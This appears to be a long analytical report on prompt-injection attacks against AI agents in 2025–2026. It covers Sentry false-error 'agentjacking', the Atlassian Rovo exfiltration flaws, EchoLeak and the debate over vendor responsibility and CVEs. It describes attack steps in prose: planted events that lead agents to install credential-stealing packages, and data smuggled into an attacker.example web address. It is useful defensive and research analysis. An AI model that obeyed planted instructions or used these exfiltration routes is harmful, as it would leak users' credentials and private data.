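Scripts on an online shop's checkout page run in the shopper's browser, so the browser has to report any crash. The page therefore contains a Data Source Name (DSN), an address that includes a public key and the number of the shop's Sentry project. Sentry's *Data Source Name (DSN)* documentation calls these addresses "safe to keep public" because they only let people submit events, not read anything.

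Sentry concedes on the same page that anyone can use a DSN to send a company whatever information they like, but says this is rare. Customers can block particular network addresses or replace the key, though the new key has to go into the same public web page as the old one.

Leaving the key public was reasonable when only people read the reports. In *DSN private/public*, an older thread on Sentry's forum, a developer asked whether to hide the key and was told that the worst anyone could do was send events. A false event might waste a few minutes of a developer's time, but an agent that can run commands may follow instructions written in the event.

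Others had noticed the risk before Tenet. In July 2025, Willison listed error logs among the places where text could be planted. In February 2026, Snyk audited a Sentry add-on for agents and rated it a medium risk because it returned request data, tags and stack traces that outsiders could influence (skills.sh, *sentry-issue-resolver*, 2026).

### From a false event to the developer's credentials

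Tenet and The Hacker News (2026) describe the attack in roughly these steps:

1. The attacker copies the DSN from a company's website.
2. The attacker sends Sentry a false error event. Its message contains headings and a code block that imitate the layout of Sentry's own output, including a "Resolution" section with a command to run.
3. A developer asks a coding agent to fix the unresolved Sentry issues.
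4. The agent fetches the event through Sentry's official tool server, which returns the attacker's text as part of the result.
5. The agent runs the command, which downloads a package from npm and starts it.
6. The package can now read cloud keys, GitHub tokens and other credentials on the developer's computer and send them to the attacker.

The planted text doesn't have to mention secrets, because the package it recommends searches for them. Cursor had refused Zenity's first Jira ticket because it asked for API keys, but Tenet's text only recommended a diagnostic tool, which developers often install while fixing an error. Once the package starts, the model can't stop the theft by refusing a later step, because the package is an ordinary program that runs without the model.

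### A server that only returned data

In the GitHub and Supabase demonstrations, the official tool server carried out the whole theft at the agent's request, whereas Sentry's server only delivered the planted text.

| Attack | What the official server did | What read the private data | How the data could leave | Would a read-only server stop it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub, `pacman` | Returned the issue, read private files and opened a pull request | GitHub's server | The pull request | Yes, unless the agent had another way to send data out |
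| Supabase support ticket | Returned the ticket, read the token table and added a row | Supabase's server | The new row in the ticket | Yes, with the same exception |
| Sentry | Returned the false event | The package on the developer's computer | The package's own internet connection | No |

Limiting the agent's Sentry token wouldn't protect the credentials either, because they are on the developer's computer, not in Sentry. A company that reviewed only Sentry's server could reasonably conclude that it was low risk. The danger comes from connecting it to an agent with command-line access, which can read private data and send it out.

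Zenity's attack on Cursor is the closest precedent, but it required the agent to find the token and send it out itself, whereas Tenet's method requires the agent to make only one mistake.

### Tenet's measurements

An attack counted as successful if an agent ran a harmless test package that Tenet controlled, according to Hackread's *Agentjacking*. This is a fair test of whether an attacker could run code, because a malicious package would have had the same permissions. It doesn't show that an attacker would have obtained useful credentials every time, because some developers keep few credentials on their computers and some networks would block a malicious package from sending them out.

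The Hacker News reports that Tenet tested the attack against more than 100 organisations and succeeded 85% of the time. But according to Tenet's summary, more than 100 agents acted on the false errors, so that figure counts successes. If the 85% rate came from the same tests, Tenet must have made at least 118 attempts.

They more likely came from separate tests. When Tenet sent an event to another company, it could see whether its package ran. If the package didn't run, Tenet would have had no obvious way to tell whether an agent had ignored the instructions or no agent had read them. Researchers can measure an exact success rate much more easily on agents they operate themselves. The 85% is therefore probably a laboratory figure, and the press reports don't give the number of runs or the models behind it.

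It is still far above the 0.2% that Anthropic reported for Claude Opus 5 a month later on a different set of attacks. Tenet's request looked like normal debugging, which may explain part of the gap. Muncaster (2026) reports in *New "Agentjacking" Attacks Could Hijack AI Coding Agents* that agents ran the package even when instructed in their prompts to ignore untrusted data. Supabase's warnings around query results rely on the same kind of instruction.

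The figure of 2,388 organisations counts those with a valid DSN that would accept a false event. Vaughan (2026), in *Agentjacking*, a guide for users of OpenAI's Codex agent, says that Tenet found them through passive reconnaissance and that 71 were among the million most popular websites. Sentry tells customers that DSNs can be public, so an organisation could be on the list just for using Sentry as intended.

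The count of 2,388 organisations doesn't show how many use coding agents, connect them to Sentry or let them run commands. The 100 successes equal about 4% of 2,388, but the success rate is unknown because the reports don't give the number of these organisations that received a false event.

### Code on other companies' computers

The agents that ran the package belonged to real organisations, including hosting providers, start-ups and, according to TechSpective (2026), a company worth roughly $250 billion. Tenet's evidence is therefore stronger in one respect than the demonstrations on test accounts, because it reflects the settings, permissions and habits of actual users. Invariant Labs had to assume that its user had chosen "Always Allow".

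None of the reports says the organisations agreed to take part. According to VPNCentral's *Agentjacking Attack Can Trick AI Coding Agents Into Running Hacker-Controlled Code*, Tenet said it used "responsible disclosure headers" and collected limited metadata instead of stealing secrets. Such headers can identify who sent an event, but they don't give the sender permission to run a program on an employee's computer.

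Tenet also wrote that it had done all this while "breaching nothing". That is true of Sentry, which accepted the events as designed, but it is harder to accept for the developers' computers if nobody there had agreed to the test. The package was harmless, but researchers would normally ask before running code on someone else's machine. The reports don't name the organisations, so outsiders can't ask them what they knew or check the count.

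### Disclosure dates and claims of real attacks

Tenet reported the problem to Sentry on 3 June 2026 and published its post on 9 June. Muncaster's article appeared on 11 June, before the disclosure dates of 12 or 17 June that some accounts give.

The later date may come from Hackread, which reported that Tenet's validation period ended on 17 June. Tenet's post already contained the figures of 2,388 organisations and more than 100 agents on 9 June, so either testing continued after publication or the date refers to something else. Tenet also launched commercially on 17 June, according to *Ex-Cisco researchers launch Tenet Security to lock down rogue AI agents* (Riley, 2026). The company had a clear interest in making the attack sound new and hard to stop.

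There is no confirmed case of a criminal using the method. Tech Jacks Solutions' *Agentic AI News* described an "active exploit campaign" tracked through 21 June, but according to the site's own notes, the claim had a single source and the supporting links didn't work. The site may have mistaken Tenet's tests for a criminal campaign. CPO Magazine's *Over 100 AI Coding Agents Taken Over Via New “Agentjacking” Attack* says it is unclear whether anyone has used the method in a real attack. A theft could be hard to recognise afterwards because the record on the developer's computer would show a coding agent installing a package, which is routine.

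### "Technically not defensible"

Sentry acknowledged the report and added a filter that blocks one string of text, which Hackread identifies as the validation text from Tenet's test. Sentry declined to fix the root cause, calling the problem "technically not defensible", and left the fix to the companies that make models and agents. The phrase comes from Tenet's account of the exchange, so it is unclear how much Sentry meant it to cover.

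The filter was worth adding because it stops people who copy Tenet's test exactly, but an attacker can get around it by choosing another package name or rewriting the message.

Vaughan considers Sentry's answer "architecturally honest", and he is right about how Sentry collects events. Visitors can read any key that a site sends to their browser, so an attacker can copy it. Sentry also can't reliably tell false crash reports from real ones, because real reports come from strangers' browsers too. Blocking every event that contains a command or a code block would discard real errors from software that handles commands and code.

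The Next Web's *Agentjacking* objects that the filter treats the symptom and that "nobody wants to own the fix". It accepts that the weakness isn't Sentry's alone, since support tickets and GitHub issues can mislead agents in the same way. But Sentry has much more control over its tool server than over the crash reports it receives, because it decides which fields the agent gets and how they look. The server could remove formatting from the message and field names so that a stranger couldn't imitate Sentry's own headings. It could also label those fields as untrusted, as GitHub's server now does with issues. The model might still follow instructions in plain text, but a separate program could use the label to block commands after the agent had read such an event.

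Customers can also reduce the risk by using separate projects for browser and server code, each with its own DSN, as Sentry already recommends. The server's DSN doesn't have to appear on a web page, and an agent limited to the server project would never see an event sent with the website's DSN. That agent also couldn't help with browser crashes, and a server error may still quote something that a visitor typed into a form. To exploit this, an attacker would have to cause a real error that repeats the planted text, which is harder than sending a false one.

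Sentry is only one example of the problem. Barak Sternberg, one of the Tenet researchers, told TechSpective that Cloudflare and Datadog also use public keys that let people write data.

### Limits on the agent's command line

Controls on what an agent can run and where it can connect can detect this attack, and Tenet's own free tool, agent-jackstop, relies on them. Tenet nonetheless described the attack as "invisible to every security control" because the developer had authorised the agent and each tool it used. That may be true of firewalls that only check for intruders or scanners that only check for known malware.

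The tool is a set of configurations for Cursor and Claude Code. Forkast describes its main protection as blocking all internet destinations except those on an approved list, which stops both the download of the package and the transfer of stolen data. The tool also requires approval for every command, blocks programs from reading common credential folders and tells the agent to distrust tool output. The last measure is probably the weakest, because agents in Tenet's tests ignored similar instructions.

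A person who reads the command before it runs can also stop the attack. VPNCentral notes that Sentry designed its tool server for coding agents with a human in the loop. The reports don't include how many developers in Tenet's tests had turned off approvals and how many had approved the command. A diagnostic package is easy to approve during debugging, especially when it seems to come from Sentry.

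Codex blocks network access by default while it runs commands, according to Vaughan, so the planted command couldn't download its package. But Vaughan's sample configuration allows connections to the npm registry and GitHub. Tenet's package came from npm, and Guan's attack on Copilot had already used GitHub to get stolen keys past a firewall. A developer who copied these settings would let the command download the package and might let the package send out credentials.

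Vaughan also proposes a script that looks for suspicious commands before each call to Sentry's server. As written, it checks the agent's request to Sentry, but the planted command is in Sentry's reply. It would be more useful if it ran before each shell command, to check what the agent is about to execute. An attacker could still reword the command to avoid the patterns it looks for. Keeping production credentials off the computer where the agent works is more reliable, because the package then can't steal them from it.

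## July and August 2026: Atlassian Rovo and the routes by which data leaves

An attacker who steers Rovo, Atlassian's built-in assistant, has only the tools that Atlassian provides, whereas in the Sentry attack the data could leave through a program the attacker had written. Rovo answers employees' questions using data from Jira, Confluence and any other services the company has connected, with the permissions of the employee who asks. In July and August 2026, researchers published two separate ways to make it send private data to an outside website. Neither involved Atlassian's official tool server, which now also has Rovo in its name.

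### RovoBlast: a question inside a link

Rovo's chat page accepted a question as part of its web address, so a link could open the chat with the question already filled in. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) reports that Rovo also ran the question, without a warning or confirmation. An attacker could write the question and send the link to an employee, and Rovo would run it when the employee clicked. The address normally contains an organisation's ID, but if the attacker left this blank, Atlassian would fill in the victim's, so the same link could work at any company that used Rovo.

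The researcher loacker described the theft on Bugcrowd, a platform for reporting vulnerabilities, in *One-Click Data Exfiltration via rovoChatPrompt URL Parameter (Confluence / Rovo)*. The link contained instructions for Rovo to find private content, put it in the address of an image on the attacker's website and load the image. The attacker's server received the content when Rovo requested the image. In the demonstration, this exposed an API key from a Confluence page. SecurityWeek's *Critical One-Click Vulnerability in Atlassian’s Rovo AI Exposed Enterprise Data* adds that the researchers took Jira tickets and SharePoint content that included personal data.

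Varonis wrote that the attack needed no jailbreak, meaning a prompt built to defeat a model's safeguards. That is slightly overstated, because loacker disguised the request, though thinly, as a question about a picture to get around Rovo's guardrails.

Rovo treated the text in the link as the employee's own question, so even a model that ignored every instruction in documents and tickets would have followed it. This also gave Atlassian a specific flaw to fix, and it changed its servers so that such links no longer run an attacker's instructions. loacker had reported the flaw on 4 November 2025, and Atlassian paid $6,000 in January. It deployed the fix on 8 July 2026, eight months after the report, which is a long time for a flaw that took one click to exploit and that customers couldn't patch themselves.

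### PromptArmor's attack: the page-opening tool that stayed on

PromptArmor, which had reported the Slack AI flaw in 2024, hid its instructions to Rovo in a file. In *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, an employee uploads a guide to managing a backlog and asks Rovo to organise their Jira tickets. The hidden text makes Rovo add what it finds in Jira and Confluence to a web address on the attacker's site and then open that address. Rovo did this without asking for approval, and the attacker could read the tickets and documents in the site's logs. When the employee reopened the chat, it showed only suggested ticket updates.

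The attack still worked after an administrator had switched off web search for the whole organisation. The setting stopped Rovo from searching, but Rovo could still use the tool for opening search results, and that tool would open any address, including one Rovo had just composed. An administrator could reasonably have assumed that switching off web search would stop Rovo from contacting outside websites.

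PromptArmor called the attack "zero-click". The Hacker News (2026) objects that the employee still has to give Rovo the poisoned content and ask for something, and that only the final step happens without approval. The objection is correct, but it would matter less if the instructions arrived in a support ticket. PromptArmor says this would also work, but it demonstrated the attack only with an uploaded file.

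| | RovoBlast | PromptArmor's attack |
|---|---|---|
| What the employee does | Clicks a link while logged in | Uploads a file and makes a routine request |
| Data taken in demonstrations | Confluence, Jira and SharePoint | Jira and Confluence |
| Data within reach | Whatever Rovo can open for that employee | The same |
| Reported to Atlassian | 4 November 2025 | 23 May 2026 |
| Made public | July 2026, with a fuller account in August | 5 August 2026 |
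| Status | Fixed on 8 July 2026 | No confirmed fix |

Atlassian gave PromptArmor a case number in May. PromptArmor followed up on 4 June and 29 July, heard nothing more and published while the attack still worked. The Hacker News found no sign that the July fix for links had affected the attack. Neither flaw had a CVE as of 8 August, and neither report describes an attack on a real company.

Atlassian may since have partly fixed the problem. Atlassian's *Manage web access for Rovo* describes two switches, one for searching the web and one for opening public web pages. The second looks like the control that PromptArmor found missing. But both are on by default, and no one appears to have published a test of the attack with the second turned off.

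Atlassian told SecurityWeek that this class of attack affects AI systems across the industry, and advised customers to check that any content they give its apps comes from a trusted source. A support desk can't follow that advice for its tickets, although an employee can for a file from the internet.

Varonis recommends disconnecting services that Rovo doesn't need and keeping legal, personnel and financial records out of its reach. Removing Rovo altogether is harder. Administrators can block it app by app, but The Hacker News notes that its search and chat stay available on a site as long as any Jira app there has Rovo on. Atlassian's *Manage Rovo access for Enterprise* adds that Jira Service Management, the helpdesk product, may need extra configuration.

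### A web address or a comment

Both Rovo attacks sent the data out in a web address. An address can contain almost any text, and web servers normally record every requested address. If an agent has read the made-up token EXAMPLE-7Q and requests `attacker.example/EXAMPLE-7Q`, the attacker gets the token even if no such page exists. The request can come from a browser that loads an image (as in the GitLab Duo attack), a Slack link preview, or the agent's own tool.

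With a write-back channel, the agent writes the token into a pull request, comment, ticket reply or database row, and the attacker opens the page and reads it.

| | Data in a web address | Write-back |
|---|---|---|
| What the attacker needs | A website whose logs they can read | A ticket, page or row that they can read |
| What the agent needs | Any tool or display feature that requests web addresses | Permission to write in that place |
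| Room for data | The length of an address, per request | Often a whole document at once |
| Effect of a list of approved websites | Blocks it, unless the attacker controls or can misuse an approved site | None, because the agent needs the service for its work |
| What remains afterwards | At most a log entry wherever the request passed | The leaked text, until someone removes it |

A network allowlist permits connections only to approved sites. An agent that fixes bugs on GitHub needs access to GitHub, so a stolen file can leave over the same connection as the bug fix. The allowlist can't distinguish a private repository from a public one, or an internal note from a reply to a customer. In the threat model for its agentic workflows, GitHub describes how a compromised agent could upload secrets to the web or encode them in public issues, pull requests and comments. The firewall in that design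 addresses only the web uploads.

With write-back, the attacker also doesn't have to run a server or register a domain, so there is no unfamiliar address for a security team to notice and block. Whoever planted the instructions in a support ticket already has access to the place where the answer will appear. In Invariant Labs' demonstration, the answer appeared in a public pull request, so the attacker didn't need an account to read it.

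Besides an allowlist, a fairly clean remedy for the web-address route is to let the tool open only addresses that appeared in full in the user's message or in the result of a trusted tool. Rovo would then have refused the address in PromptArmor's attack, because Rovo had put that address together itself. If uploaded files counted as trusted, an attacker could still use one to list a ready-made address for each letter and have the agent open them in the order that spells out a secret. Stealing a single key this way would take dozens of requests, which is slow and much easier to spot.

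There is no equivalent rule for comments. A company connects an agent to its helpdesk so that the agent will write new text based on what it has read.

### What write-back leaves behind

Atlassian records every call to its official tool server in the customer's audit log, with the name of the tool, the action and the user. After an attack like Cato's on the helpdesk, the log would show that a support engineer had searched Jira, read several items and commented on a ticket. The same engineer's agent may have done that fifty times that day, and those three fields would not distinguish the theft from the legitimate work.

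The log is even less useful when agents connect with an API token. It then records the account behind the token, which several employees may share, so an investigator may not be able to tell whose session read the planted ticket.

The order of the calls is a better clue. If an agent reads an outsider's ticket, searches unrelated projects and replies a few seconds later, that sequence is worth checking. A company could set an alert for this pattern, but it would go off often because good support agents also search widely, for example to find out whether other customers have the same fault.

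Once someone suspects a leak, write-back is the easier of the two routes to investigate. The leaked text is in the ticket, usually below the instructions that caused the leak, so the company can see what it lost and who could read it. By contrast, after PromptArmor's attack, the clearest record of the stolen documents was in the attacker's logs. Rovo runs in Atlassian's cloud, so Rovo's request probably never passed through the customer's firewall. Varonis similarly complains that RovoBlast's steps look like "normal research" in the records.

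An attacker may try to remove the evidence. Atlassian's *Supported tools*, which lists everything its server offers as of November 2026, shows that the tools for deleting Jira items and comments are off until an administrator enables them. But the tool that adds comments can also edit them, so after copying the first reply, an attacker could plant a second message that gets an agent to overwrite that reply.

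### When read-only mode works

Removing an agent's write tools closes the write-back channel in that service, provided that the vendor has correctly identified the tools that can expose data. Some tools give outsiders access to content without moving it, so a scanner that checks outgoing text for secrets would find nothing to block. Atlassian's server has one that turns on a public link for a Confluence page and another that can make a video public in Loom, its video service. Atlassian classes both as write tools, so read-only access removes them. No published attack has used them, and an attacker would still have to learn the page's address.

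Rovo's page-opening tool, by contrast, reads web pages and changes nothing in Jira or Confluence. An administrator could have removed every tool Rovo uses to edit anything and still left PromptArmor's route open.

A second tool server can also reopen a route for data to leave. Suppose a support engineer's agent has read-only access to Atlassian and write access to GitHub, where it files bug reports. An attacker plants a ticket with instructions to read a confidential Confluence page and post the text as an issue in the attacker's public repository. If the agent complies, Atlassian's server handles only read requests, and GitHub's server receives ordinary prose, which its check for leaked keys and passwords would let through. Each server is configured sensibly, but neither receives the calls made to the other. Atlassian gives a related warning that switching off web access in Rovo may not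 block a connected tool.

Read-only mode is also a serious limitation for anyone whose agent does more than answer questions. An agent that sorts new issues can't apply a label. A support agent can draft a reply, but an engineer has to paste it into the ticket. *Rovo Admin*, a feature request on Atlassian's issue tracker, describes a customer that wanted to stop agents from changing the working hours logged in Jira. Blocking the tools that make those changes would also have stopped the agents from creating, editing and commenting on issues. The November tool list still describes permissions by group.

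### Letting an agent write without letting it leak

A company whose agent needs write tools can split the job between two sessions, one that reads tickets and private data but has no write tools, and another that has write tools but can't access the tickets or private data. The safe outputs in GitHub's agentic workflows follow this pattern, but in GitLost the private README still passed from the reading side to the writing side inside an approved comment.

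The division is therefore only as secure as the limit on what crosses it. For an agent that sorts issues, that limit can be very tight. If the reading session may pass on only one of eight labels, each issue can carry at most three bits, because 2³ = 8. A random 40-character token of letters and digits contains about 238 bits, so an attacker would need at least 80 issues to extract it, and the agent would have to obey every time. The drawback is that the agent can't ask the person who reported a bug for missing details.

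This arrangement is much less useful for a support agent, whose replies are free text. No short list of permitted answers would satisfy customers. An employee would have to transfer the relevant facts from one session to the other, which is most of the work the agent was meant to save.

Human approval is the more common safeguard, and its effectiveness depends heavily on what the approval prompt displays. The Model Context Protocol recommends showing a call's inputs, which for a comment on a Jira ticket are probably the ticket number and the text. The reviewer also needs to know who can read the comment and, ideally, which parts came from outside the ticket. A busy engineer probably wouldn't stop at a ticket number, but would stop if the prompt said "This reply goes to an outside customer and quotes two internal pages."

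Atlassian's server routes its less common tools through three general calls, one for reading, one for writing and one for destructive actions. The agent's software handles confirmation, and this split lets it allow reading without a prompt but ask before writing. However, the call for writing covers both starring a page and publishing it on the web. A user who chooses "Always Allow" to stop the prompts about starring pages may have approved publication as well.

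If a helpdesk sends 300 replies a day and a reviewer spends 20 seconds on each, the reviews take 100 minutes a day. The study of Claude Code's users suggests that the reviewer's attention would fade well before the end. Requiring approval only for replies that contain material from outside the customer's own ticket would cut the number considerably. An unattended agent that sorts issues has no one to ask, so its comments would wait until a maintainer came back. Approval for writes alone would not have stopped the Rovo leak, because Rovo leaked the data by opening a page.

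Blocking an agent from writing to public places after it has read private data covers more of these cases. This relies on information-flow control, the labelling method that FIDES uses. Microsoft applies such labels to emails, files, documents and chats, and treats a link to an unapproved website as another public channel. With links treated this way, the same rule would stop the Rovo attacks, the `pacman` pull request and the Confluence page posted to GitHub. The rule has to run in the software that operates the agent, because only that software handles the calls to every server. GitHub has been adding to its agentic workflows a block on data flows from private to public repositories and a way for maintainers to exempt particular servers.

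This is the best of the three controls for an agent that sorts public issues. It doesn't restrict the agent at all if the agent never opens anything private. But once the agent consults an internal design document about one bug, it can't comment publicly on that bug or any later one in the same session, so maintainers would want a fresh session for every issue.

A support agent needs the finer labels that list who may read each piece of data, so that it can tell Ana about her own order and nobody else's. Internal troubleshooting notes remain a problem even then, because customers aren't allowed to read them but a good answer often paraphrases them. An employee would have to approve each of those replies, or the company would have to mark the notes as safe to share.

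## Product vulnerability or inherent agent behaviour

When Invariant Labs disclosed the Pac-Man attack, it described a "critical vulnerability" in GitHub's official server but also wrote that the server's code had no flaw. The label matters because customers expect a vendor to fix a product vulnerability, announce the fix and perhaps pay whoever found it. If the leak is instead inherent in how agents behave, customers have to protect themselves.

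### Three places to put the blame

Invariant concluded that the leak is a "fundamental architectural issue" in agent systems. Supabase took the same position in September 2025, calling the problem "a property of how LLMs interact with tools" that arises with any company's server. In the same post, Supabase accepted that it still has to help its users deploy safely.

Others blame the vendor's design. In the July 2025 Hacker News thread about Supabase, a commenter called emilsedgh argued that companies normally put a layer of code between a database and its clients to control who may see what, and that Supabase had released a tool server without one because everyone now needed a tool server. The best evidence for this view is Willison's observation that GitHub's and Supabase's servers each supply the whole lethal trifecta. Willison doesn't fully share the view, though, because he doubts that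 a vendor can make such a server safe.

A third group blames the operator, who chose the agent's permissions. In the thread about Invariant Labs' post, losvedir wrote that anyone who gives a model a credential should assume it can do whatever the credential allows. In this view, the owner of `pacman` gave the agent too much access.

People debating this question tend to overlook the maker of the agent program. The commenter tptacek thought the Supabase leak was "a problem with Cursor, not with LLMs", because Cursor put customers' tickets and the ability to run database queries in the same context.

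### Why a parameterised query has no full equivalent

Supabase's critics kept returning to SQL injection, a flaw that looks similar and has a complete fix. Suppose a support site looks up tickets by customer name. A careless program pastes the name into the text of a command:

`SELECT * FROM tickets WHERE customer = 'Ana'`

A visitor can type a quotation mark followed by more SQL. The quotation mark ends the name early, and the database runs the rest as part of the command. With a parameterised query, the program first sends the command with a gap in it:

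`SELECT * FROM tickets WHERE customer = ?`

The database parses the structure of this command first, so whatever the visitor typed can only fill the gap. A strange name finds no tickets, and it can't add a condition or open another table.

A language model never fixes the structure of its task in this way. It estimates the probability of each next token from all the tokens before it, P(*x*ₜ₊₁ | *x*₁, …, *x*ₜ). Those earlier tokens include both the developer's instructions and the customer's ticket. A marker such as "customer text starts here" is also only a series of tokens. Training can make the model give the marker a lot of weight, which is why such markers help, but the ticket still affects the prediction.

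An agent also has to let the data it reads affect what it does. A support agent that reads a ticket about failed logins on Tuesday should look at Tuesday's login records, whereas a site never wants a customer's name to change the command it runs. TeMPOraL, another commenter in the Supabase thread, argued that people really want the model to work out which parts of the text the user would have wanted it to act on, rather than to keep instructions and data apart. He considered that problem unsolvable in general.

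His example was a clerk who has to type out pages of meaningless test data and finds a line saying that people are trapped in a laboratory and someone should call an ambulance. Most clerks would call, and most employers would want them to. rtpg replied that if the page said to throw the paper away, any serious person would type that sentence and carry on. Both examples seem right, and they suggest that a narrow task makes people less likely to follow instructions they find in the data, but doesn't rule it out.

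ethbr1 thought the answer was old and simple. Callers once got free long-distance calls by whistling the tones that controlled the telephone network, until the phone companies moved the control signals to a separate channel. ethbr1 compared this to a post office where only letters in red envelopes can change delivery times. vidarh replied that such a rule works well if the clerk can't read the letters. A clerk who does read them may come across one in a green envelope from someone claiming to be the postmaster, who has run out of red ones and says somebody will die unless the times change.

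ethbr1 still had a good point, which was that ordinary code can always sit between a model's output and an action, and refuse the action. TeMPOraL's reply was that the hard cases involve actions the user is allowed to take but wouldn't want in this context. The pull request in `pacman` is exactly such a case.

tptacek proposed a design that comes closer to a parameterised query. One model context reads tickets and produces a structured request, ordinary code checks it, and a second context that has never seen the tickets turns it into SQL. saurik objected that any free-text field in the request could carry instructions across. Even a field for the customer's name would do, because an attacker can register an instruction as their name. tptacek would have the code discard anything that didn't fit a strict format, and accept that some harmless requests would fail too. The two agreed that the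 way to settle it was to build the system and attack it, but the thread contains no such test.

tptacek also identified what makes SQL's remedy so unusual. A parameterised query blocks the attack and still accepts every legitimate input. The known designs for agents, including CaMeL, block attacks by giving up some legitimate work.

Willison objected to partial defences because an attacker can keep trying until something works, so "99% is a failing grade" in application security. A developer who forgets to parameterise a query can correct it and be fully protected again, but a filter trained on examples never gives full protection. TeMPOraL thought this standard was too strict, since people accept imperfect security almost everywhere outside computing. He would use models only where some failures are tolerable.

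David C reached much the same conclusion for the National Cyber Security Centre that December. He wrote that a language model may not be a good fit for a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk. He called the comparison with SQL injection dangerous because security staff who accept it will look for a single fix. He was particularly wary of products that claim to "stop" prompt injection and of filters that block known phrases, which an attacker can reword endlessly.

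His history of SQL injection is less comforting to vendors than the rest of his argument. The attacks peaked around 2010, when most websites already depended on SQL and few were protected against injection. They became rare after a decade of breaches led to better techniques and better defaults. An equivalent technique may never exist for agents, but vendors can improve their defaults now.

Parameterised queries also wouldn't have stopped the theft from Supabase, because the agent wrote a valid query for the private table. Anthropic's reference Postgres server did have a SQL injection flaw that a code change could fix, and Datadog Security Labs could point users to a patched version maintained by Zed Industries. No similar code change would make Cursor's model ignore instructions in a ticket.

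### Promises, repairs, defaults and costs

The vendors mostly kept their explicit promises. GitHub showed the private README only to an account entitled to read it, and Postgres applied its policies to every query that wasn't exempt. But someone who marks a repository as private also expects that a stranger can't obtain its contents by filing an issue. Vendors rarely write this expectation down, and whether most of these cases are product vulnerabilities depends on whether it counts as a security boundary.

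PromptArmor's attack on Rovo still worked with web search switched off, so an explicit setting failed. Neither the nature of language models nor the employee's permissions excuse that failure.

The two sides often mean different things when they discuss whether vendors can fix the problem. As Invariant said, GitHub can't make Claude ignore a stranger's issue, but a vendor can prevent the leak by removing one part of the trifecta. Even when a company runs the agent itself, its fix may be only partial. Microsoft rated Zenity's attack on a Copilot Studio customer-service agent as critical and released a fix within two months. The researchers wrote, in an account published by the Cloud Security Alliance, that their tests indicated the fix was mainly a classifier that now recognised the text of their attack.

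Supabase had the least safe default, since a user who added no settings gave the agent write access to every project. GitHub's defaults are harder to judge because the server included all the tools needed for the theft, but the owner chose how much the token could access. In GitLost, the default was safe, and someone had to add a token to give the agent access to the other repositories.

The best argument against leaving everything to the operator is that others can sometimes prevent an attack with less effort. If Supabase made read-only mode the default, it would protect every new user, including those who haven't learned about the attack, and people who build apps would have to change one setting. GitHub is different because only the owner knows which repositories a job needs, though GitHub's long list of permissions makes the choice more work than losvedir's comment implies. In the Sentry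 case, the maker of the coding agent is best placed to prevent the attack, since it can block network access for commands whatever service the bad advice came from.

| Case | Did the vendor break an explicit promise? | Can the vendor prevent the leak? | Was the default unsafe? | Who could prevent it most cheaply? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub, `pacman` | No | Yes, at the cost of useful issues or of writing | Partly | The owner, with a narrower token |
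| Supabase support ticket | No | Yes, for its own server, with read-only access | Yes | Supabase |
| Sentry false error | No | Only partly | Not in Sentry's server | The maker of the coding agent |
| GitLost | No | Yes, by requiring approval for risky replies | No | The maintainer, if GitHub warned them |
| Rovo's page-opening tool | Yes, in effect | Yes | Yes | Atlassian |

The operator's permissions explain GitLost fairly well but the Supabase leak poorly. The architectural view is weakest for products like Rovo, where one company sells the agent and its tools and stores the data, so it can't blame anyone else's software.

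### EchoLeak and the Copilot flaws of 2026

Microsoft is in this position with Microsoft 365 Copilot, its assistant for email and documents. A flaw called EchoLeak let an outsider steal data from Copilot by sending the victim one email. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, described it as a longer version of a familiar attack, in which planted text makes an assistant put private data in a web address. The security company Aim Labs found the flaw and reported it in January 2025, and Microsoft had fixed it by June.

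Microsoft assigned the flaw the identifier CVE-2025-32711. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot 'zero-click' vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* gives its severity as 9.3 out of 10 and reports Microsoft's statement that nobody had exploited it and that customers didn't need to act.

Reddy and Gujral explain in *EchoLeak* that the email attack not only manipulated the model but also chained several bypasses, including those of a classifier Microsoft had built to catch injected instructions and a feature that removes links. EchoLeak therefore fits the view that CVEs are for failed controls.

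The Copilot Studio flaw that Microsoft patched in January 2026 is less clearly a product vulnerability, because the agent seems to have simply followed instructions in a form. Microsoft still assigned it a CVE, and Capsule Security called that decision "highly unusual", according to Claw Times.

In a third case, from June 2026, researchers combined a prompt injection with two ordinary web flaws in Copilot's enterprise search, according to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026). One click on a link could expose the victim's emails, security codes and files. Varonis called the flaw critical, while Microsoft scored it 6.5 because the victim had to click. Varonis found another Copilot flaw that, much like RovoBlast, ran a prompt from a crafted link, and Microsoft patched it in August, according to the OECD's *Microsoft Copilot Vulnerability Exposed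 Sensitive Data via AI Prompt Injection* (2026).

### Do CVEs follow a failed control?

A plausible hypothesis is that vendors assign a CVE when a specific control fails, but rarely when an agent merely follows instructions in text it reads. The table shows how vendors handled 15 cases. "None reported" means that the accounts of the case mention no CVE, though one may exist.

| Case | What went wrong | CVE | Vendor's response |
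|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub, `pacman`, May 2025 | Agent obeyed an issue | None | No public statement; later protections announced as features |
| EchoLeak, June 2025 | Email got past a classifier and a link filter | CVE-2025-32711 | Patch |
| Atlassian helpdesk, June 2025 | Agent obeyed a ticket | None reported | Advice to customers |
| Supabase, July 2025 | Agent obeyed a ticket | None reported | Warnings, documentation, optional settings |
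| Cursor and Jira, August 2025 | Agent obeyed a ticket | None reported | Closed as a known issue, with advice |
| Copilot Studio form, January 2026 | Agent obeyed a form | CVE-2026-21520 | Patch |
| Claude, Gemini and Copilot in GitHub workflows, April 2026 | Agents obeyed planted text; Copilot's protections also failed | None reported | Bounties of $100, $1,337 and $500; partial changes |
| Copilot enterprise search, June 2026 | Injection combined with two web flaws | CVE-2026-42824 | Patch |
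| Sentry, June 2026 | Agent obeyed an error report | None reported | Filter for one string; refused a deeper fix |
| GitHub lockdown mode, permission check, 2026 | Check gave wrong answers | None found | Patch |
| GitHub lockdown mode, shared connection, 2026 | Server used one person's login for everyone's checks | CVE-2026-48529 | Patch |
| GitLost, July 2026 | Agent obeyed an issue | None reported | No change to the code |
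| RovoBlast, July 2026 | A link ran a prompt without asking | None by 8 August | $6,000 bounty and a patch |
| Rovo's page-opening tool, August 2026 | A setting left a tool switched on | None by 8 August | No confirmed fix |
| SalesBleed, September 2026 | Filter misread web addresses | None | Patches |

The April attacks involved both kinds of failure, so they don't help to separate the two. One of the seven cases in which an agent simply obeyed has a CVE, compared with three of the seven in which something more specific broke. The hypothesis is right that obedience rarely results in a CVE, but a broken control often doesn't result in one either.

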